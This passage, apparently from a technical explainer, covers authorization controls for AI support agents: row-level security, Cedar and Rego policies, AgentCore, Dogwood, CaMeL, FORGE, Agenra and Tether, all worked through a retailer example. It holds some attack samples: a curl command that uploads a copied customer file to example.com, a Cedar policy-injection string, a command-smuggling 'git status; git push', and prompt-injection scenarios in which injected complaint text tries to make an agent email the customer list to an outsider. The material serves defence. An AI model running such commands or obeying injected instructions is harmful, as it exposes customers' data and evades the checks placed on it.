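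Researchers have discussed this problem for over two decades. *Access Control by Query Modification* (Byun, 2004) describes a student who asks for the average grade and receives the average of their own grades. *Extending query rewriting techniques for fine-grained access control* (Rizvi, Mendelzon and colleagues, 2004) proposes a system that rejects such queries. It accepts a query only if an equivalent one can be written using only the data the user may see. This is more flexible than looking for a particular condition, but no algorithm can decide in general whether two SQL queries are equivalent, so any such checker will reject some acceptable queries.

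Wang, Yu and colleagues (2006), in *On the Correctness Criteria of Fine-Grained Access Control in Relational Databases*, explain what silent narrowing gets right and wrong. Let *A*(*D*, *P*, *Q*) be the answer to query *Q* on database *D* under policy *P*. The method is secure if

*A*(*D*, *P*, *Q*) = *A*(*D*′, *P*, *Q*)

whenever *D* and *D*′ differ only in data that *P* hides. Row-level security should meet this condition, since changing another customer's order has no effect on what customer 88 receives. Wang and colleagues also require that the answer contain nothing that would be missing from the unrestricted answer. The list of products fails this second test. They designed a method that meets both conditions, but it was practical only for tables of moderate size, around 10,000 rows.

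The retailer can use both approaches. If the checker requires the customer condition, row-level security does not change the results of accepted queries, but it still hides other customers' orders when the checker misses something.

### Setting up row-level security

According to PostgreSQL's documentation, the database normally evaluates the policy for each row before any conditions in the user's query, and a table with row security enabled but no policies shows no rows. However, Crunchy Data's *Row Security Policies* explains that superusers always bypass the policies, and that a table's owner normally does too. The agent therefore needs its own account that owns no tables. The checker should also restrict which functions a query may call, because PostgreSQL has a built-in function that can change `app.customer` from inside a `SELECT`.

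PostgreSQL can raise an error instead of silently hiding rows. According to postgresqlco.nf's *row security*, any query to which a policy would apply fails if the setting `row_security` is off. This suits backups, where missing rows could go unnoticed until someone needs them. It doesn't suit the support agent, because even a query with the correct customer condition would fail. According to a PostgreSQL commit message, turning the setting off only causes these errors and doesn't bypass the policies, so an agent that did so would not gain access to anything.

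### Limits on the number of rows

The retailer can also limit how many rows a query returns. A cap of 50 would stop the agent from copying the whole orders table in one query, but would still allow `SELECT AVG(delivery_days) FROM orders`, which reads every row and returns only one.

For changes to data, the number of affected rows is more informative. Suppose the retailer lets the agent mark orders as returned:

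```sql
UPDATE orders SET status = 'returned' WHERE id = 4417;
```

If the model leaves out the last condition, the command marks every order the agent can change. Even if a checker requires a `WHERE` clause, it can't tell from the text how many rows a condition will match. The orchestrator can instead run the command in a transaction, a group of changes that the database either keeps or undoes as a whole. The database reports how many rows the command changed, and the orchestrator keeps the change only if the number is one.

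A one-row limit would not catch a command that changes the wrong order. Undoing a transaction reverses only changes made inside the database. If the update had triggered an email to the customer, that email would already have been sent.

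## Policy engines for single requests

A refund request is easier to check than a shell command or a query because it contains only a function name, an order number and an amount. The retailer could put the 500-dollar cap in the refund tool's code. But once a company has dozens of tools, rules scattered through their code are hard to review, and changing a rule means changing a program. A policy engine is a separate program that keeps the rules in one place. It takes a request and a set of policies and returns allow or deny.

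### From tool call to authorization request

Cedar, the AWS policy language that Rex uses, describes a request in four parts. The principal is whoever is asking, the action is what they want to do, the resource is what they want to do it to, and the context holds any other facts. Suppose customer 88 has logged in and the model proposes `refund(order=4417, amount=80)`. The orchestrator could build this request:

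| Part | Value | Origin |
|---|---|---|
| Principal | `Customer::"88"` | The customer's login |
| Action | `Action::"refund"` | The model's tool call |
| Resource | `Order::"4417"` | The model's tool call |
| Context | `{amount: 80}` | The model's tool call |

An injected instruction can change anything the model writes, which here means everything except the principal. The principal comes from a token that the retailer's login service issues and signs. The token contains claims, such as the customer's number, and altering a claim invalidates the signature. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* gives the example of a bulk discount for platinum customers who order at least 50 items. The customer's tier is a signed claim, but the model writes the quantity.

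A policy can safely check an argument the model wrote if the tool then acts on the same value. If the model understates the refund amount to get past the check, the customer receives less. But an argument such as `manager_approved=true` is not evidence of approval, because the model can write it whether or not a manager has approved the refund. Facts like this have to come from a record the agent cannot edit. Likewise, the orchestrator should look up who placed order 4417 and pass the answer to the policy engine.

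AWS's hosted service, AgentCore Policy, builds the request slightly differently. It runs in a gateway, a server between the agent and its tools. In an example from the *Policy Overview*, a model requests a refund of 450 dollars. The user's number in the token becomes the principal, the token's claims become tags on that principal, the model's arguments go into the context, and the gateway is the resource. According to *Schema constraints*, the arguments are the only part of the context that an ordinary policy can read, so it can't look up who placed an order.

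The retailer could supply that fact with an interceptor, a program that rewrites a request before Cedar evaluates it. HKU SPACE's *Secure AI agents with Policy and Lambda interceptors in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* explains that the gateway calls the tool with the rewritten request, so Cedar checks the same request the tool receives. The interceptor becomes part of the trusted base.

An engine can also run inside the agent's software. Classmethod's *I tried writing tool authorization for Strands Agents with Cedar policies* describes an agent framework that evaluates Cedar policies before each tool call. This is easier to install than a gateway, but a script running in the same process might be able to alter the engine. A gateway avoids that problem, but it checks only the calls that pass through it.

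### Cedar's decision rule

Each Cedar policy starts with an effect, `permit` or `forbid`. A scope follows, which limits the principals, actions and resources it covers, and then any further conditions. The retailer might write these two:

```cedar
permit (
  principal is Customer,
  action == Action::"refund",
  resource is Order
)
when {
  resource.customer == principal &&
  context.amount > 0 &&
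  context.amount <= 500
};

forbid (
  principal is Customer,
  action == Action::"refund",
  resource is Order
)
when { resource.chargeback };
```

The first permits refunds of up to 500 dollars on the customer's own orders. The second forbids a refund if the order has a chargeback, which means the customer's bank is already taking the money back.

Let *P* be the set of permits that apply to a request and *F* the set of forbids that apply. Cedar allows the request if and only if

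*P* ≠ ∅ and *F* = ∅.

Here are three requests from customer 88, who placed both orders:

| Request | Permit applies | Forbid applies | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 80 dollars on order 4417 | Yes | No | Allow |
| 620 dollars on order 4417 | No | No | Deny |
| 80 dollars on order 4502, which has a chargeback | Yes | Yes | Deny |

Cedar denies the second request because no policy permits it, even though none forbids it. It denies the third because a forbid overrides any permit, including one that a colleague adds later. The order of the policies makes no difference.

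The comparison with 500 works if the tool takes whole dollars. If it accepts cents, AgentCore converts the amount to Cedar's decimal type, and the condition becomes `context.input.amount.lessThanOrEqual(decimal("500.00"))`. Such boundaries are easy to get slightly wrong. AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* gives the refund limit as "$500 or less", but its sample policy tests whether the amount is `< 500`, so it denies a refund of exactly 500 dollars.

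Cedar has no general loops, and a policy cannot read files, contact the network or change data. Evaluation therefore always finishes, and the same request gets the same answer if the policies and data stay the same. In *Cedar*, Cutler, Disselkoen and colleagues (2024) modelled the language in Lean and proved the decision rule's main properties, such as that a forbid always overrides a permit. The engine that companies run is a separate program written in Rust. Cedar's developers compare it with the Lean model on large numbers of random inputs, and by 2024 their random testing had found nearly two dozen bugs.

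### When a policy causes an error

Suppose the retailer started recording chargebacks last year, so older orders have no `chargeback` field. Cedar gets an error when it evaluates `resource.chargeback` for one of them. According to Cedar's documentation, the engine ignores any policy that causes an error and decides using the rest. Ignoring a permit policy is cautious, but ignoring a forbid policy removes the prohibition, so the retailer's other policy allows the refund. According to a comment in Cedar's source code, the developers debated other ways to handle errors but have implemented only this one.

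Cedar's validator can find this mistake before anyone uses the policy. It needs a schema, which lists the types of principal and resource, their attributes, and the actions that apply to them. The validator then checks each policy against every combination of types the schema allows. It catches misspelled names, comparisons between incompatible types, and optional attributes that a policy reads without first checking that they exist. If the schema marks `chargeback` as optional, the validator rejects the retailer's forbid. The obvious repair is:

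```cedar
when { resource has chargeback && resource.chargeback }
```

This passes validation, but Cedar still allows refunds on old orders, because the condition is false for them. To deny those refunds, the retailer should write:

```cedar
unless { resource has chargeback && !resource.chargeback }
```

Now the forbid applies unless the record shows that there is no chargeback. The validator accepts both versions, so the author has to decide what missing data should mean.

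Cutler and colleagues proved that a validated policy never fails because of a wrong type or a missing attribute, as long as the data matches the schema and includes every entity involved. Other errors remain possible. A forbid that tests `context.amount + context.fee > 500` causes an error if the sum is too large for a 64-bit number, and Cedar would then ignore the rule meant to stop the refund. The retailer's cap avoids this problem because it is a condition of the permit, so an error there would leave the request with no permit and Cedar would deny it.

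### Checking every possible request

A policy can pass validation and still allow or deny the wrong requests. To find such mistakes, a tool called Cedar Analysis translates policies into formulas for an SMT solver. The principal, resource and context become unknowns, and the solver either finds values that make a formula true or proves that none exist.

AWS gives the example of a refund policy for gold and platinum customers whose author wrote "and" instead of "or". With *t* for the customer's tier and *a* for the amount, the question for the solver is roughly whether

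∃*t*, *a*: *t* = "Gold" ∧ *t* = "Platinum" ∧ *a* ≤ 1000.

No value of *t* satisfies both equations, so the policy can never apply. The solver can also look for a request in the policy's scope to which the policy does not apply. If it finds none, the policy applies to every request in its scope. An example is a policy whose only condition is that a quantity is either at least 100 or less than 100.

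Some problems appear only when policies are combined. In another of AWS's examples, one policy permits refunds under $100 for gold customers, and another forbids refunds under $500 for the same customers. Each policy makes sense by itself, but the second blocks every refund that the first permits.

To compare two sets of policies, *A* and *B*, the solver looks for a request *r* that only one of them allows:

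∃*r*: allow_A(*r*) ≠ allow_B(*r*).

If *A* permits refunds with `amount <= 500` and *B* with `amount < 500`, the solver returns a refund of exactly 500 dollars, which the two sets decide differently. If it proves that no such request exists, the two sets make the same decision on every request. This comparison is useful for reviewing policy changes, which can have counterintuitive effects. AWS describes a discount policy with an exception for limited editions. Someone changes the exception to apply only to orders of more than 200 items. This narrows the exception, so an order for 73 limited-edition items now gets the discount, even though the added condition looks like a restriction.

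The retailer can check its cap in a similar way by asking whether

∃*r*: allow(*r*) ∧ amount(*r*) > 500.

If there is no such request, no combination of the retailer's policies permits a larger refund. The retailer still has to enter the right number, because the solver would not detect that somebody had typed 5,000 instead of 500.

SMT solvers often fail to reach an answer when a formula contains "for all", so Cedar's designers kept the language small enough to avoid it. Groups made this difficult. A Cedar user can belong to a team, and that team to a larger team, but no team can contain itself, even indirectly. Without this rule, the solver might report an impossible case in which teams A and B belong to each other. Stating the rule for all teams would require a "for all", so when Cutler and colleagues translate policies into formulas, they state it only for the teams and other entities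 that the policies mention, which they proved is enough. The solver can therefore, in principle, correctly answer every question translated this way. In their tests, a question took 75.1 milliseconds on average. The proof was on paper in 2024, and a Lean version was in progress.

### Rego and Open Policy Agent

Open Policy Agent (OPA) is an open-source engine that accepts any request written in JSON, a common format for structured data. Its language, Rego, extends Datalog, in which an author writes facts and rules for deriving further facts. The current version of Open Policy Agent's *Policy Language* gives the basic form of a rule as a name, a value and a body of conditions. If all the conditions hold, the name takes the value, which is `true` unless the author specifies another. The retailer's refund policy looks like this:

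```rego
package support

default allow := false

allow if {
  input.tool == "refund"
  input.amount > 0
  input.amount <= 500
  order := data.orders[input.order]
  order.customer == input.customer
  order.chargeback == false
}
```

`input` is the request, including the customer's number, which the orchestrator fills in from the login. `data` holds information from elsewhere, in this case the orders. A refund of 80 dollars on order 4417 meets every condition, so `allow` is true. A refund of 620 dollars on the same order fails the comparison with 500, and a refund on order 4502 fails the last line because of the chargeback. In both cases the rule produces no value, which Rego calls undefined, and the `default` line supplies `false`. Without that line, OPA would return an empty result, which the calling program would have to handle.

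Undefined values can also cause trouble inside a rule. If an old order has no `chargeback` field, `order.chargeback == false` is undefined and OPA denies the refund. An author could easily have written the more natural `not order.chargeback`, but `not` succeeds whether the expression after it is false or undefined, so OPA would allow refunds on old orders. The result is the same as with Cedar's ignored forbid, except that no error occurs.

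AI SDK's *Policy-Based Tool Approvals*, part of the documentation of a library for building agents, lists three ways OPA can get data: loading it together with the policy, fetching updates at intervals, and querying another service during evaluation. The policy can then use facts that the calling program did not send. However, a stored copy of the data may be out of date, and another service's answer may change from one minute to the next.

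Rego can also search lists of records. This is helpful with Terraform, a tool that sets up servers and databases from a written description and can list its planned changes as JSON before making them. Backend Engineering Strategy Tools' *OPA & Rego* names these plans among OPA's possible inputs. If the retailer let an agent manage its servers, it could use this rule:

```rego
deny contains "deletes a database" if {
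  some change in input.resource_changes
  change.type == "aws_db_instance"
  "delete" in change.change.actions
}
```

The `some` keyword makes OPA look for any planned change that meets both conditions. Cedar can test whether a set contains particular values, but it has no general loop for examining records.

This flexibility makes Rego harder to analyse. Rego bans `while` loops and rules that refer to themselves so that evaluation will finish (Open Policy Agent, *rego_recursion_error*). But *Rego Policy Language for OAuth 2.0 Authorization* (Liu, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) points out that no algorithm can determine, for every pair of Rego policies, whether one allows only requests that the other also allows. Rego rules can combine tables of data much as SQL queries do, and SQL has a similar limitation.

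A tool could still compare simple policies such as the refund rule. For other policies, Rego users have to rely more on testing. OPA's test command could confirm that a refund of 500 dollars passes and one of 501 fails. If a colleague added a second `allow` rule that permitted refunds of any size for orders placed on Sundays, the tests would miss it unless somebody thought to try a Sunday order, whereas a solver analysing the equivalent Cedar policies would find such an order.

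### Comparisons between the languages

Cutler and colleagues found that Cedar evaluated requests 42.8 to 80.8 times faster than Rego in three sample applications. Most of the researchers worked at AWS, which develops Cedar. The difference in speed matters little to the retailer, since either engine is usually much faster than the model whose calls it checks.

Outside firms have done two security comparisons, both paid for by companies with products of their own. Teleport's *Security Benchmarking Authorization Policy Engines* says that AWS hired the security firm Trail of Bits in 2024 to study Cedar, Rego and OpenFGA, a language for permissions based on relationships between users and objects. Trail of Bits listed threats to such languages, identified features that reduce those threats and recommended improvements, but it did not build a set of tests that others could run.

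Another security firm, Doyensec, later built a set of 27 tests for policy engines. Teleport, which sells access-control software, funded the work and had its own engine included. Doyensec predicted some of the results instead of running the tests.

| Engine | Passed | Failed | Not applicable | Results predicted |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cedar | 17 | 4 | 6 | 9 |
| OpenFGA | 17 | 6 | 4 | 9 |
| Teleport | 17 | 4 | 6 | 7 |
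| Rego | 7 | 18 | 2 | 7 |

Rego's low score partly reflects what the tests cover. Several of them penalise functions that contact the network or interact with the host system, and Cedar has no such functions. Some results also look unreliable. Rego failed a test with 1,000 sets but passed the same test with 10,000 and 100,000. Teleport advises against using the benchmark to rank engines and recommends it for tracking one engine over time.

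Individual results are more useful than the totals. Rego failed the tests on undefined values and on negating them, which matches the problem with `not order.chargeback`. Cedar failed a test of whether validation catches overflow and missing entities. Rego also failed to enforce a deny rule when an error occurred. Doyensec predicted that Cedar would fail in the same way, which is consistent with Cedar's documented behaviour.

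### Policy engines in agent products

AWS made AgentCore Policy generally available in thirteen of its regions on March 3, 2026 (AWS, *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available*, 2026). Once the retailer attaches a policy engine, the gateway blocks every tool call that no policy permits. AgentCore generates the Cedar schema from the tools' descriptions and validates each policy against it. It also runs Cedar Analysis on the full set of policies and rejects changes that appear to contain logical errors. Policy authors can describe a rule in English and have a model draft the policy.

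The gateway also hides tools that the current user could never call. It evaluates the policies with the arguments left unknown, and if they would deny the call whatever the arguments, it leaves the tool off the list it sends to the agent. AWS argues that this keeps the model from attempting to call those tools. The gateway still needs to check each call, because an injected instruction could supply a hidden tool's name.

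A new policy may block legitimate requests. AWS's *Test a policy in LOG_ONLY mode* describes how to test one on real traffic without enforcing it. AgentCore counts the requests whose outcome the policy would have changed, and AWS treats a sustained count of zero as a sign that enforcing the policy won't disrupt current traffic. For a refund cap, zero might only mean that nobody has asked for more than 500 dollars yet. LOG_ONLY mode can also be set for the whole engine, in which case the gateway enforces no policies, even those marked as active. A retailer that forgot to switch it off would log refunds above the cap without blocking them.

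The same page includes a policy that blocks a message if a classifier is more than 70% confident that it contains violence. Cedar compares the classifier's score with the threshold exactly, but the score is an estimate. The policy therefore guarantees only that messages that score above 70% are blocked, and some violent messages may score lower.

Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit, which was in public preview in April 2026, also checks each tool call before it runs. Companies can write its rules in Cedar, Rego or YAML, a simple format for settings. To show why written safety instructions are not enough, Microsoft tested an agent that had no other protection. It used 45 adversarial prompts and 15 legitimate ones, and reports a violation rate of 26.67% on the adversarial prompts. The toolkit typically added less than a millisecond per call in Microsoft's measurements. As of April, it could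 not recognise a harmful sequence of calls that were each allowed, such as an oversized refund split in two.

AI SDK can run an OPA policy, written in Rego, before each tool call. The policy can allow the call, deny it or request human approval, so the retailer could have an employee review refunds above 300 dollars. The policy also receives the conversation so far, including earlier tool calls, so it can add up the refunds in that conversation. It can't enforce the daily cap this way, because the cap applies across all conversations and needs a shared record.

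By default, AI SDK runs any call that no rule matches. If the retailer added a tool for changing prices and forgot to write a rule for it, the agent could use the tool freely. Adding one line to the policy changes this default to deny. Errors already lead to denial, so a refund cannot go through if the engine crashes.

Tools that run other tools need more care. A rule against `git push`, which uploads code to a shared repository, does not stop a model that can type the same command into a shell tool. AI SDK's documentation recommends splitting the shell command into a program and its arguments, then applying the same rule to them. Its sample code splits the text at spaces, so it would read `git status; git push` as a single `git` command whose first argument is `status;`. A rule that checks the first argument for `push` would miss the second command. The documentation advises developers to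 deny any command they cannot reduce to one clean call.

### Agents that propose their own limits

In all these products, the company writes the policies. Liu and colleagues, who work at Alibaba, Cisco and Okta, propose that an agent write its own policy and request only the authority that policy covers. Their proposal extends OAuth, the standard that lets people give one service limited access to their account on another. It is an internet draft, a working document that anyone can submit to the Internet Engineering Task Force, which publishes internet standards. The draft is dated June 9, 2026, and expires on December 11, 2026. The organisation has not endorsed it.

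Suppose a customer's personal shopping agent wants to request refunds from the retailer:

1. The agent sends an authorization server a Rego policy, along with plain lists of the actions and web addresses it needs.
2. The server checks that the policy is valid Rego, defines the expected rule, and contains no dangerous operations, such as calls to other websites. It also checks that the lists stay within the permissions registered for that agent.
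3. The server decides whether these limits are appropriate. It considers the agent's registration, the company's rules and the customer's consent.
4. If it approves, it issues an access token that contains the policy or a reference to it.
5. The retailer evaluates the policy for every request the agent makes, and denies the request if the result is false or undefined.

The lists allow the authorization server to do its part without running Rego, but they don't include details such as a refund cap. An agent could propose this rule:

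```rego
allow if {
  input.action == "refund"
  not input.amount > 500
}
```

The rule caps refunds at 500 dollars only if the retailer's system puts the amount in `input.amount`. If the system uses `input.resource.amount` instead, then `input.amount` is undefined, `not` succeeds, and the rule allows a refund of any size. The list of actions contains "refund" in both cases, so it doesn't reveal the problem. Liu and colleagues mention negation as one way for a malicious agent to hide a permissive rule. They recommend a light static analysis of each proposal but leave final responsibility with the service that receives the requests. They also call for limits on the time and memory used by each evaluation.

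The retailer does not have to work out everything a proposed policy allows. It can keep its own policy and require each request *r* to pass both:

allow(*r*) = own(*r*) ∧ proposed(*r*).

A badly written or malicious proposal can then only reduce what the agent is allowed to do. The proposal is still useful, because the customer might want to authorise a single $80 refund and nothing else.

Inserting an agent's text into a larger policy is riskier. Cedar's documentation gives an example in which a program pastes a user's name into the scope of a `permit`. An attacker can instead supply `principal,action,resource); //`, which ends the policy early and turns its remaining conditions into a comment, so the policy permits everything. The attack works like the SQL injection in the order query, and the remedy is similar. Cedar has templates with slots that accept only a value.

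A parallel draft, *Cedar Profile for OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests*, defines how to include Cedar policies in the same kind of request. If an agent proposed its limits in Cedar, the server could use an SMT solver to check, before issuing a token, whether those limits allow anything the retailer's own policy forbids.

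## Rules over sequences of actions and the origin of data

A policy engine that judges each request separately can enforce the retailer's cap on single refunds but not its cap on the day's total. Suppose a group of customers talk the support agent into ten refunds of 450 dollars each. Each refund is under the 500-dollar cap, so the engine approves all ten and the retailer pays out 4,500 dollars.

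### A running total

Let *S* be the sum of the refunds the checker has approved so far that day. It approves a new refund of *a* dollars if

*S* + *a* ≤ 2,000.

| Request | Approved so far | Total with this refund | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1st | 0 | 450 | Allow |
| 2nd | 450 | 900 | Allow |
| 3rd | 900 | 1,350 | Allow |
| 4th | 1,350 | 1,800 | Allow |
| 5th | 1,800 | 2,250 | Deny |

The checker denies the other five requests for the same reason. Denied requests don't add to *S*, so the agent can still refund up to 200 dollars that day.

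The retailer could write a program that tracks *S* and passes it to Cedar with each request, but every rule about the past would then need its own code.

### Dogwood

In 2026 AWS released Dogwood, an open-source extension of Cedar whose rules can refer to earlier events. Every valid Cedar policy is also a valid Dogwood policy. According to InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls*, the interpreter evaluates each condition about earlier events and adds the result to the request's context, and Cedar then makes the decision as usual.

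AgentCore Policy supports Dogwood and keeps the history itself. AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* describes three kinds of event:

- The engine records a `request` event, with the call's arguments, when it authorises a call.
- It records a `response` event, with the arguments and the results, when the tool succeeds.
- It records an `error` event when it denies a call or the tool fails.

Adapted from one of AWS's examples, the daily limit looks like this:

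```
forbid (
  principal,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"Shop___refund",
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"support"
)
when temporal {
  exists (paid: Long).
    (sum a for (a: Long), (t: Timepoint).
      where (formerly within 24h
        (AgentCore::Action::"Shop___refund"::request{
          eventResource: resource, input.amount: a
        } && tp(t)))) == paid
    && paid > 2000
};
```

`formerly within 24h` selects the refund requests from the last 24 hours, and `sum` adds up their amounts. The variable `t` holds the time of each request, so that refunds of the same amount are counted separately. The sum includes the current request, so the fifth refund brings the total to 2,250 and the rule forbids that refund.

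The window covers the last 24 hours, which is slightly stricter than a limit per calendar day because the agent can't pay out $2,000 at 11 p.m. and another $2,000 at 1 a.m.

If the rule added up `response` events instead of `request` events, an agent could send all ten requests at once and all ten would pass, because no refund would have finished yet and the sum would be zero each time. InfoQ reports that AWS warns about the same mistake, using the example of three simultaneous transfers of 2,000 dollars under a cap of 5,000. The drawback of counting requests is that a refund counts even if the payment service rejects it.

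`formerly` can also check a single earlier event. A policy could permit a refund only if the agent had looked up the same order in the past hour, which would stop it from refunding an order number it had made up. `count` works like `sum` but counts events, so it can limit the agent to three refunds in five minutes.

`since` tests whether something has stayed true since an earlier event. AWS uses it to make an approval valid only once. In abbreviated form, the retailer's version would be:

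```
!refund::response since within 1h approve::response
```

This is true if an employee approved a refund in the last hour and no refund has finished since then. Once one finishes, the agent needs a new approval. But two refunds sent together could both pass on one approval, because neither has finished when the engine checks the other. Replacing `refund::response` with `refund::request` doesn't help, because the current request would then block itself. The orchestrator could avoid this by sending refunds one at a time.

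### Sessions and other limits

In AgentCore, each session has its own Dogwood history. The program that calls the gateway chooses the session's identifier, and a new identifier restarts the count of calls. AWS's *Temporal policies* notes that a limit on calls therefore applies only within one session.

The retailer's rule could fail without any attack on the policy engine if the orchestrator opens a new session for each conversation. Ten customers could then each receive 450 dollars, because the engine would total each session separately. To prevent this, the orchestrator would have to use the same session identifier for all refunds, and neither the model nor its scripts should be able to change it.

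Even then, the count restarts when someone adds or updates a temporal policy, because AgentCore ends the open sessions and new ones start with an empty history. If this happened after the agent had paid out 1,800 dollars, it could pay out another 2,000 that day. A strict daily cap is therefore safer if it is checked against a shared payment record that survives policy changes.

A time window can cover at most 24 hours, so the retailer can't set a weekly cap. Each policy can use up to three temporal operators, and each engine can hold up to 25 temporal policies. The gateway and its tools must be in the same AWS account and region.

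Cedar's automated analysis also can't handle Dogwood's conditions about the past. The retailer could still test sequences of requests, but it couldn't use Cedar's solver to prove that no sequence exceeds 2,000 dollars. InfoQ reports that AWS created a separate language instead of extending Cedar because of this loss. The open-source interpreter is for experiments only. A company that builds its own production version has to authenticate events, protect their timestamps and keep customers' histories separate.

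### CaMeL

A history of events shows what an agent did, but not whether data from one step ended up in another. Suppose the agent reads the customer list to answer an employee's question and later emails a supplier about a late delivery. A rule that forbids outside emails after the agent has read the list would block this email, even if it contains nothing from the list. A more precise rule needs provenance, a record of which sources a piece of data was derived from.

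CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), tracks provenance for each value in a program. One model writes the program from the user's request alone, before it has seen any emails, documents or tool results. A second model can read untrusted text but can't call tools. Suppose an employee asks the agent to refund order 4417 by the amount in the customer's complaint and to let the customer know. The first model might write:

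```python
complaint = read_complaint(order=4417)
amount = extract("What refund does the customer want?", complaint)
refund(order=4417, amount=amount)
address = lookup_email(order=4417)
send_email(address, "Your refund is on its way.")
```

An interpreter runs this program and labels each value with its sources. When it combines values, it also combines their labels. Before every tool call, it checks the labels against a policy:

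| Value | Source |
|---|---|
| `complaint` | The customer's text |
| `amount` | The customer's text, through the second model |
| `address` | The retailer's database |

If the complaint contains an instruction to email the customer list to an outsider, nothing happens, because the program has no such step. The customer can still influence `amount`, but its label shows where it came from. The policy could refer a refund to an employee whenever the amount comes from a customer's text.

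CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for a system without defences. One reason a fixed program can fail is that some requests, such as "do what this email asks", can't be written as a program until a model has read the email.

CaMeL also relies on the user being trustworthy. When a customer writes directly to the support agent, the first model writes the program from the customer's message. A dishonest customer can openly ask for harmful steps, and only the policy checks can block those steps. Unlike CaMeL, TACIT checks its rules about data when it compiles a script, before anything runs.

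### Following influence between agents

*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) describes FORGE, a monitor that tracks where data came from without requiring the agent to write a program first. FORGE attaches to existing agents and records each message, tool call and result as a node in a graph. An edge connects an event to a later one that may depend on it.

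FORGE's policies are in Datalog and, unlike Rego policies, can include rules that refer to themselves:

```
Tainted(e) :- UntrustedInput(e).
Tainted(e) :- DependsOn(e, f), Tainted(f).
```

The first rule marks an event as tainted if it is untrusted input. The second marks an event as tainted if it depends on another tainted event. Together they can follow influence through any number of steps, and evaluation still finishes because the graph is finite. A similar pair of rules tracks sensitive data, and a final rule uses both:

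```
Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).
```

Suppose the support agent reads a complaint containing an injected instruction, reads the customer list, and then tries to email an outsider. FORGE blocks the email because it depends on both earlier events.

FORGE treats each message from a model as dependent on everything in the conversation the model received. This avoids missing an influence, but the email to the supplier would also fail if the agent had read both the complaint and the list beforehand. Palumbo and colleagues therefore wrote a second policy that checks individual actions and their arguments, including whether the user asked for the action and where its target came from.

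On AgentDojo, they compared this policy with one from FIDES, a 2025 system that labels data by confidentiality and trustworthiness. The FIDES policy forbids consequential actions once the agent's context contains untrusted text. All the agents in the table used GPT-4o and received the user's request again after each set of tool results.

| Additional defence | Tasks completed without attacks | Tasks completed under attack | Successful attacks |
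|---|---|---|---|
| None | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% |
| Tool filter | 73.4% | 69.5% | 3.1% |
| FORGE with the FIDES policy | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.6% |
| FORGE with the provenance policy | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.9% |

The provenance policy was almost as secure as the FIDES policy and much less restrictive. FIDES itself can also hide tool results from the model, which might make it more useful than its policy was here. The tool filter, in which a model decides which tools to permit based on the user's request, let more attacks through but left the agent more useful than either policy. Some of the attacks counted as successful under FORGE were attempts that it had blocked. Without those, the rates fall to 0.3% and 0.2%, and the remaining attacks affected the agent's final written answer, which FORGE did not check.

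For τ²-bench's customer-service tasks, FORGE's policies encoded the companies' own rules. With enforcement, average success across three models rose from 86.3% to 87.4% on retail tasks and from 74.7% to 81.5% on airline tasks. FORGE returns an explanation with each denial, so the agent can correct its request.

FORGE can also track approvals that one agent gives another. Palumbo and colleagues tested it on a system in which five agents investigate drugs' side effects. An agent may query a US Food and Drug Administration database only after a supervisor approves that particular instance of the agent. In 15 trials, the agents made 40 unauthorised queries without FORGE and none with it. The system gave the right answer in every trial, with or without FORGE. The retailer could use a similar rule to stop an agent from relying on an approval that an employee gave to another agent.

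Datalog has no built-in notion of time, so the retailer would have to do more of its own bookkeeping for the daily limit. Dogwood expresses that limit more directly, but it doesn't track whether data from one event influenced another.

### Permissions that run out

*Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) treats permissions as something an agent can use up. For example, a policy might permit one refund on a particular order. The monitor searches the permissions in order and deducts one use from the first match that has any left. It deducts the use before the tool runs, and a failed call still counts. The monitor also uses up an employee's approval at this point, which avoids the gap in the Dogwood approval rule.

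In Cedar, making a permit broader can never cause a denial. With permissions that run out, it can. Suppose the first permission allows one refund on order B, and the second allows one on order A. The agent can refund A and then B. Now someone extends the first permission to cover either order:

1. The agent refunds A. The first permission matches, so the monitor charges it.
2. The agent tries to refund B. The first permission has no uses left, and the second covers only A, so the monitor denies the request.

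The change has blocked a legitimate sequence, yet the agent can now refund A twice.

A better rule for choosing which permission to use can't always solve this. Suppose one permission allows one refund on either A or B, and another allows one refund on either A or C. After a refund on A, the monitor has to count it against one of these permissions before anyone can know which customer will write next. If it uses the first, a later refund on B fails, and if it uses the second, a later refund on C fails.

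Shivakumar and colleagues therefore check proposed policy changes in advance. For many changes, a program written in Lean can confirm that every sequence of charges that worked under the old policy still works under the new one. In a test on 51 changes the researchers had written, the program approved all 21 that preserved the existing workflows and none of the 30 that broke one.

A change approved in this sense can still be unsafe. For example, raising an agent's email limit from one to two preserves every existing workflow but also permits a second email.

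Agenra can also require that an argument come from a particular tool. In one example, the body of an email must come from a tool that removes private fields, and identical text from another source fails the check. The first version of this rule still allowed the agent to put an attacker's text through the tool and send the result. A further rule on the tool's input prevented this.

Agenra's quotas count uses instead of dollars. To keep total refunds within 2,000 dollars, the retailer could set a quota of four refunds of at most 500 dollars each. But the monitor would then deny a fifth refund even if all five were for 20 dollars. Each counter also covers only one task, so the quota wouldn't limit refunds across a whole day's tasks.

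### Labels on files

Shell commands make provenance harder to track, because a program can move data between files without any tool call that describes the transfer. Suppose the agent runs these commands:

```
curl --json @report.txt https://example.com
cp customers.csv report.txt
curl --json @report.txt https://example.com
```

The first and third commands are identical, but only the third uploads the customer list. Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, distinguish them by giving each file a label. Tether handles a command in four steps:

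1. It runs the command in a temporary layer over the file system and holds back any network request.
2. It records the command's system calls, which are the program's requests to the operating system to open files, read them and so on.
3. It translates these calls into actions such as "copy" and "upload".
4. It checks the actions against the policy. If all of them pass, it keeps the changes and releases the request. Otherwise it discards both.

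Let σ(*r*) be the label of file *r*, on a scale from Public to Secret, and let *T* be the label of what the agent has read so far. The symbol ⊔ means the stricter of two labels. In simplified form:

- Copying *r* to *d* changes σ(*d*) to σ(*r*).
- Reading *r* changes *T* to *T* ⊔ σ(*r*).
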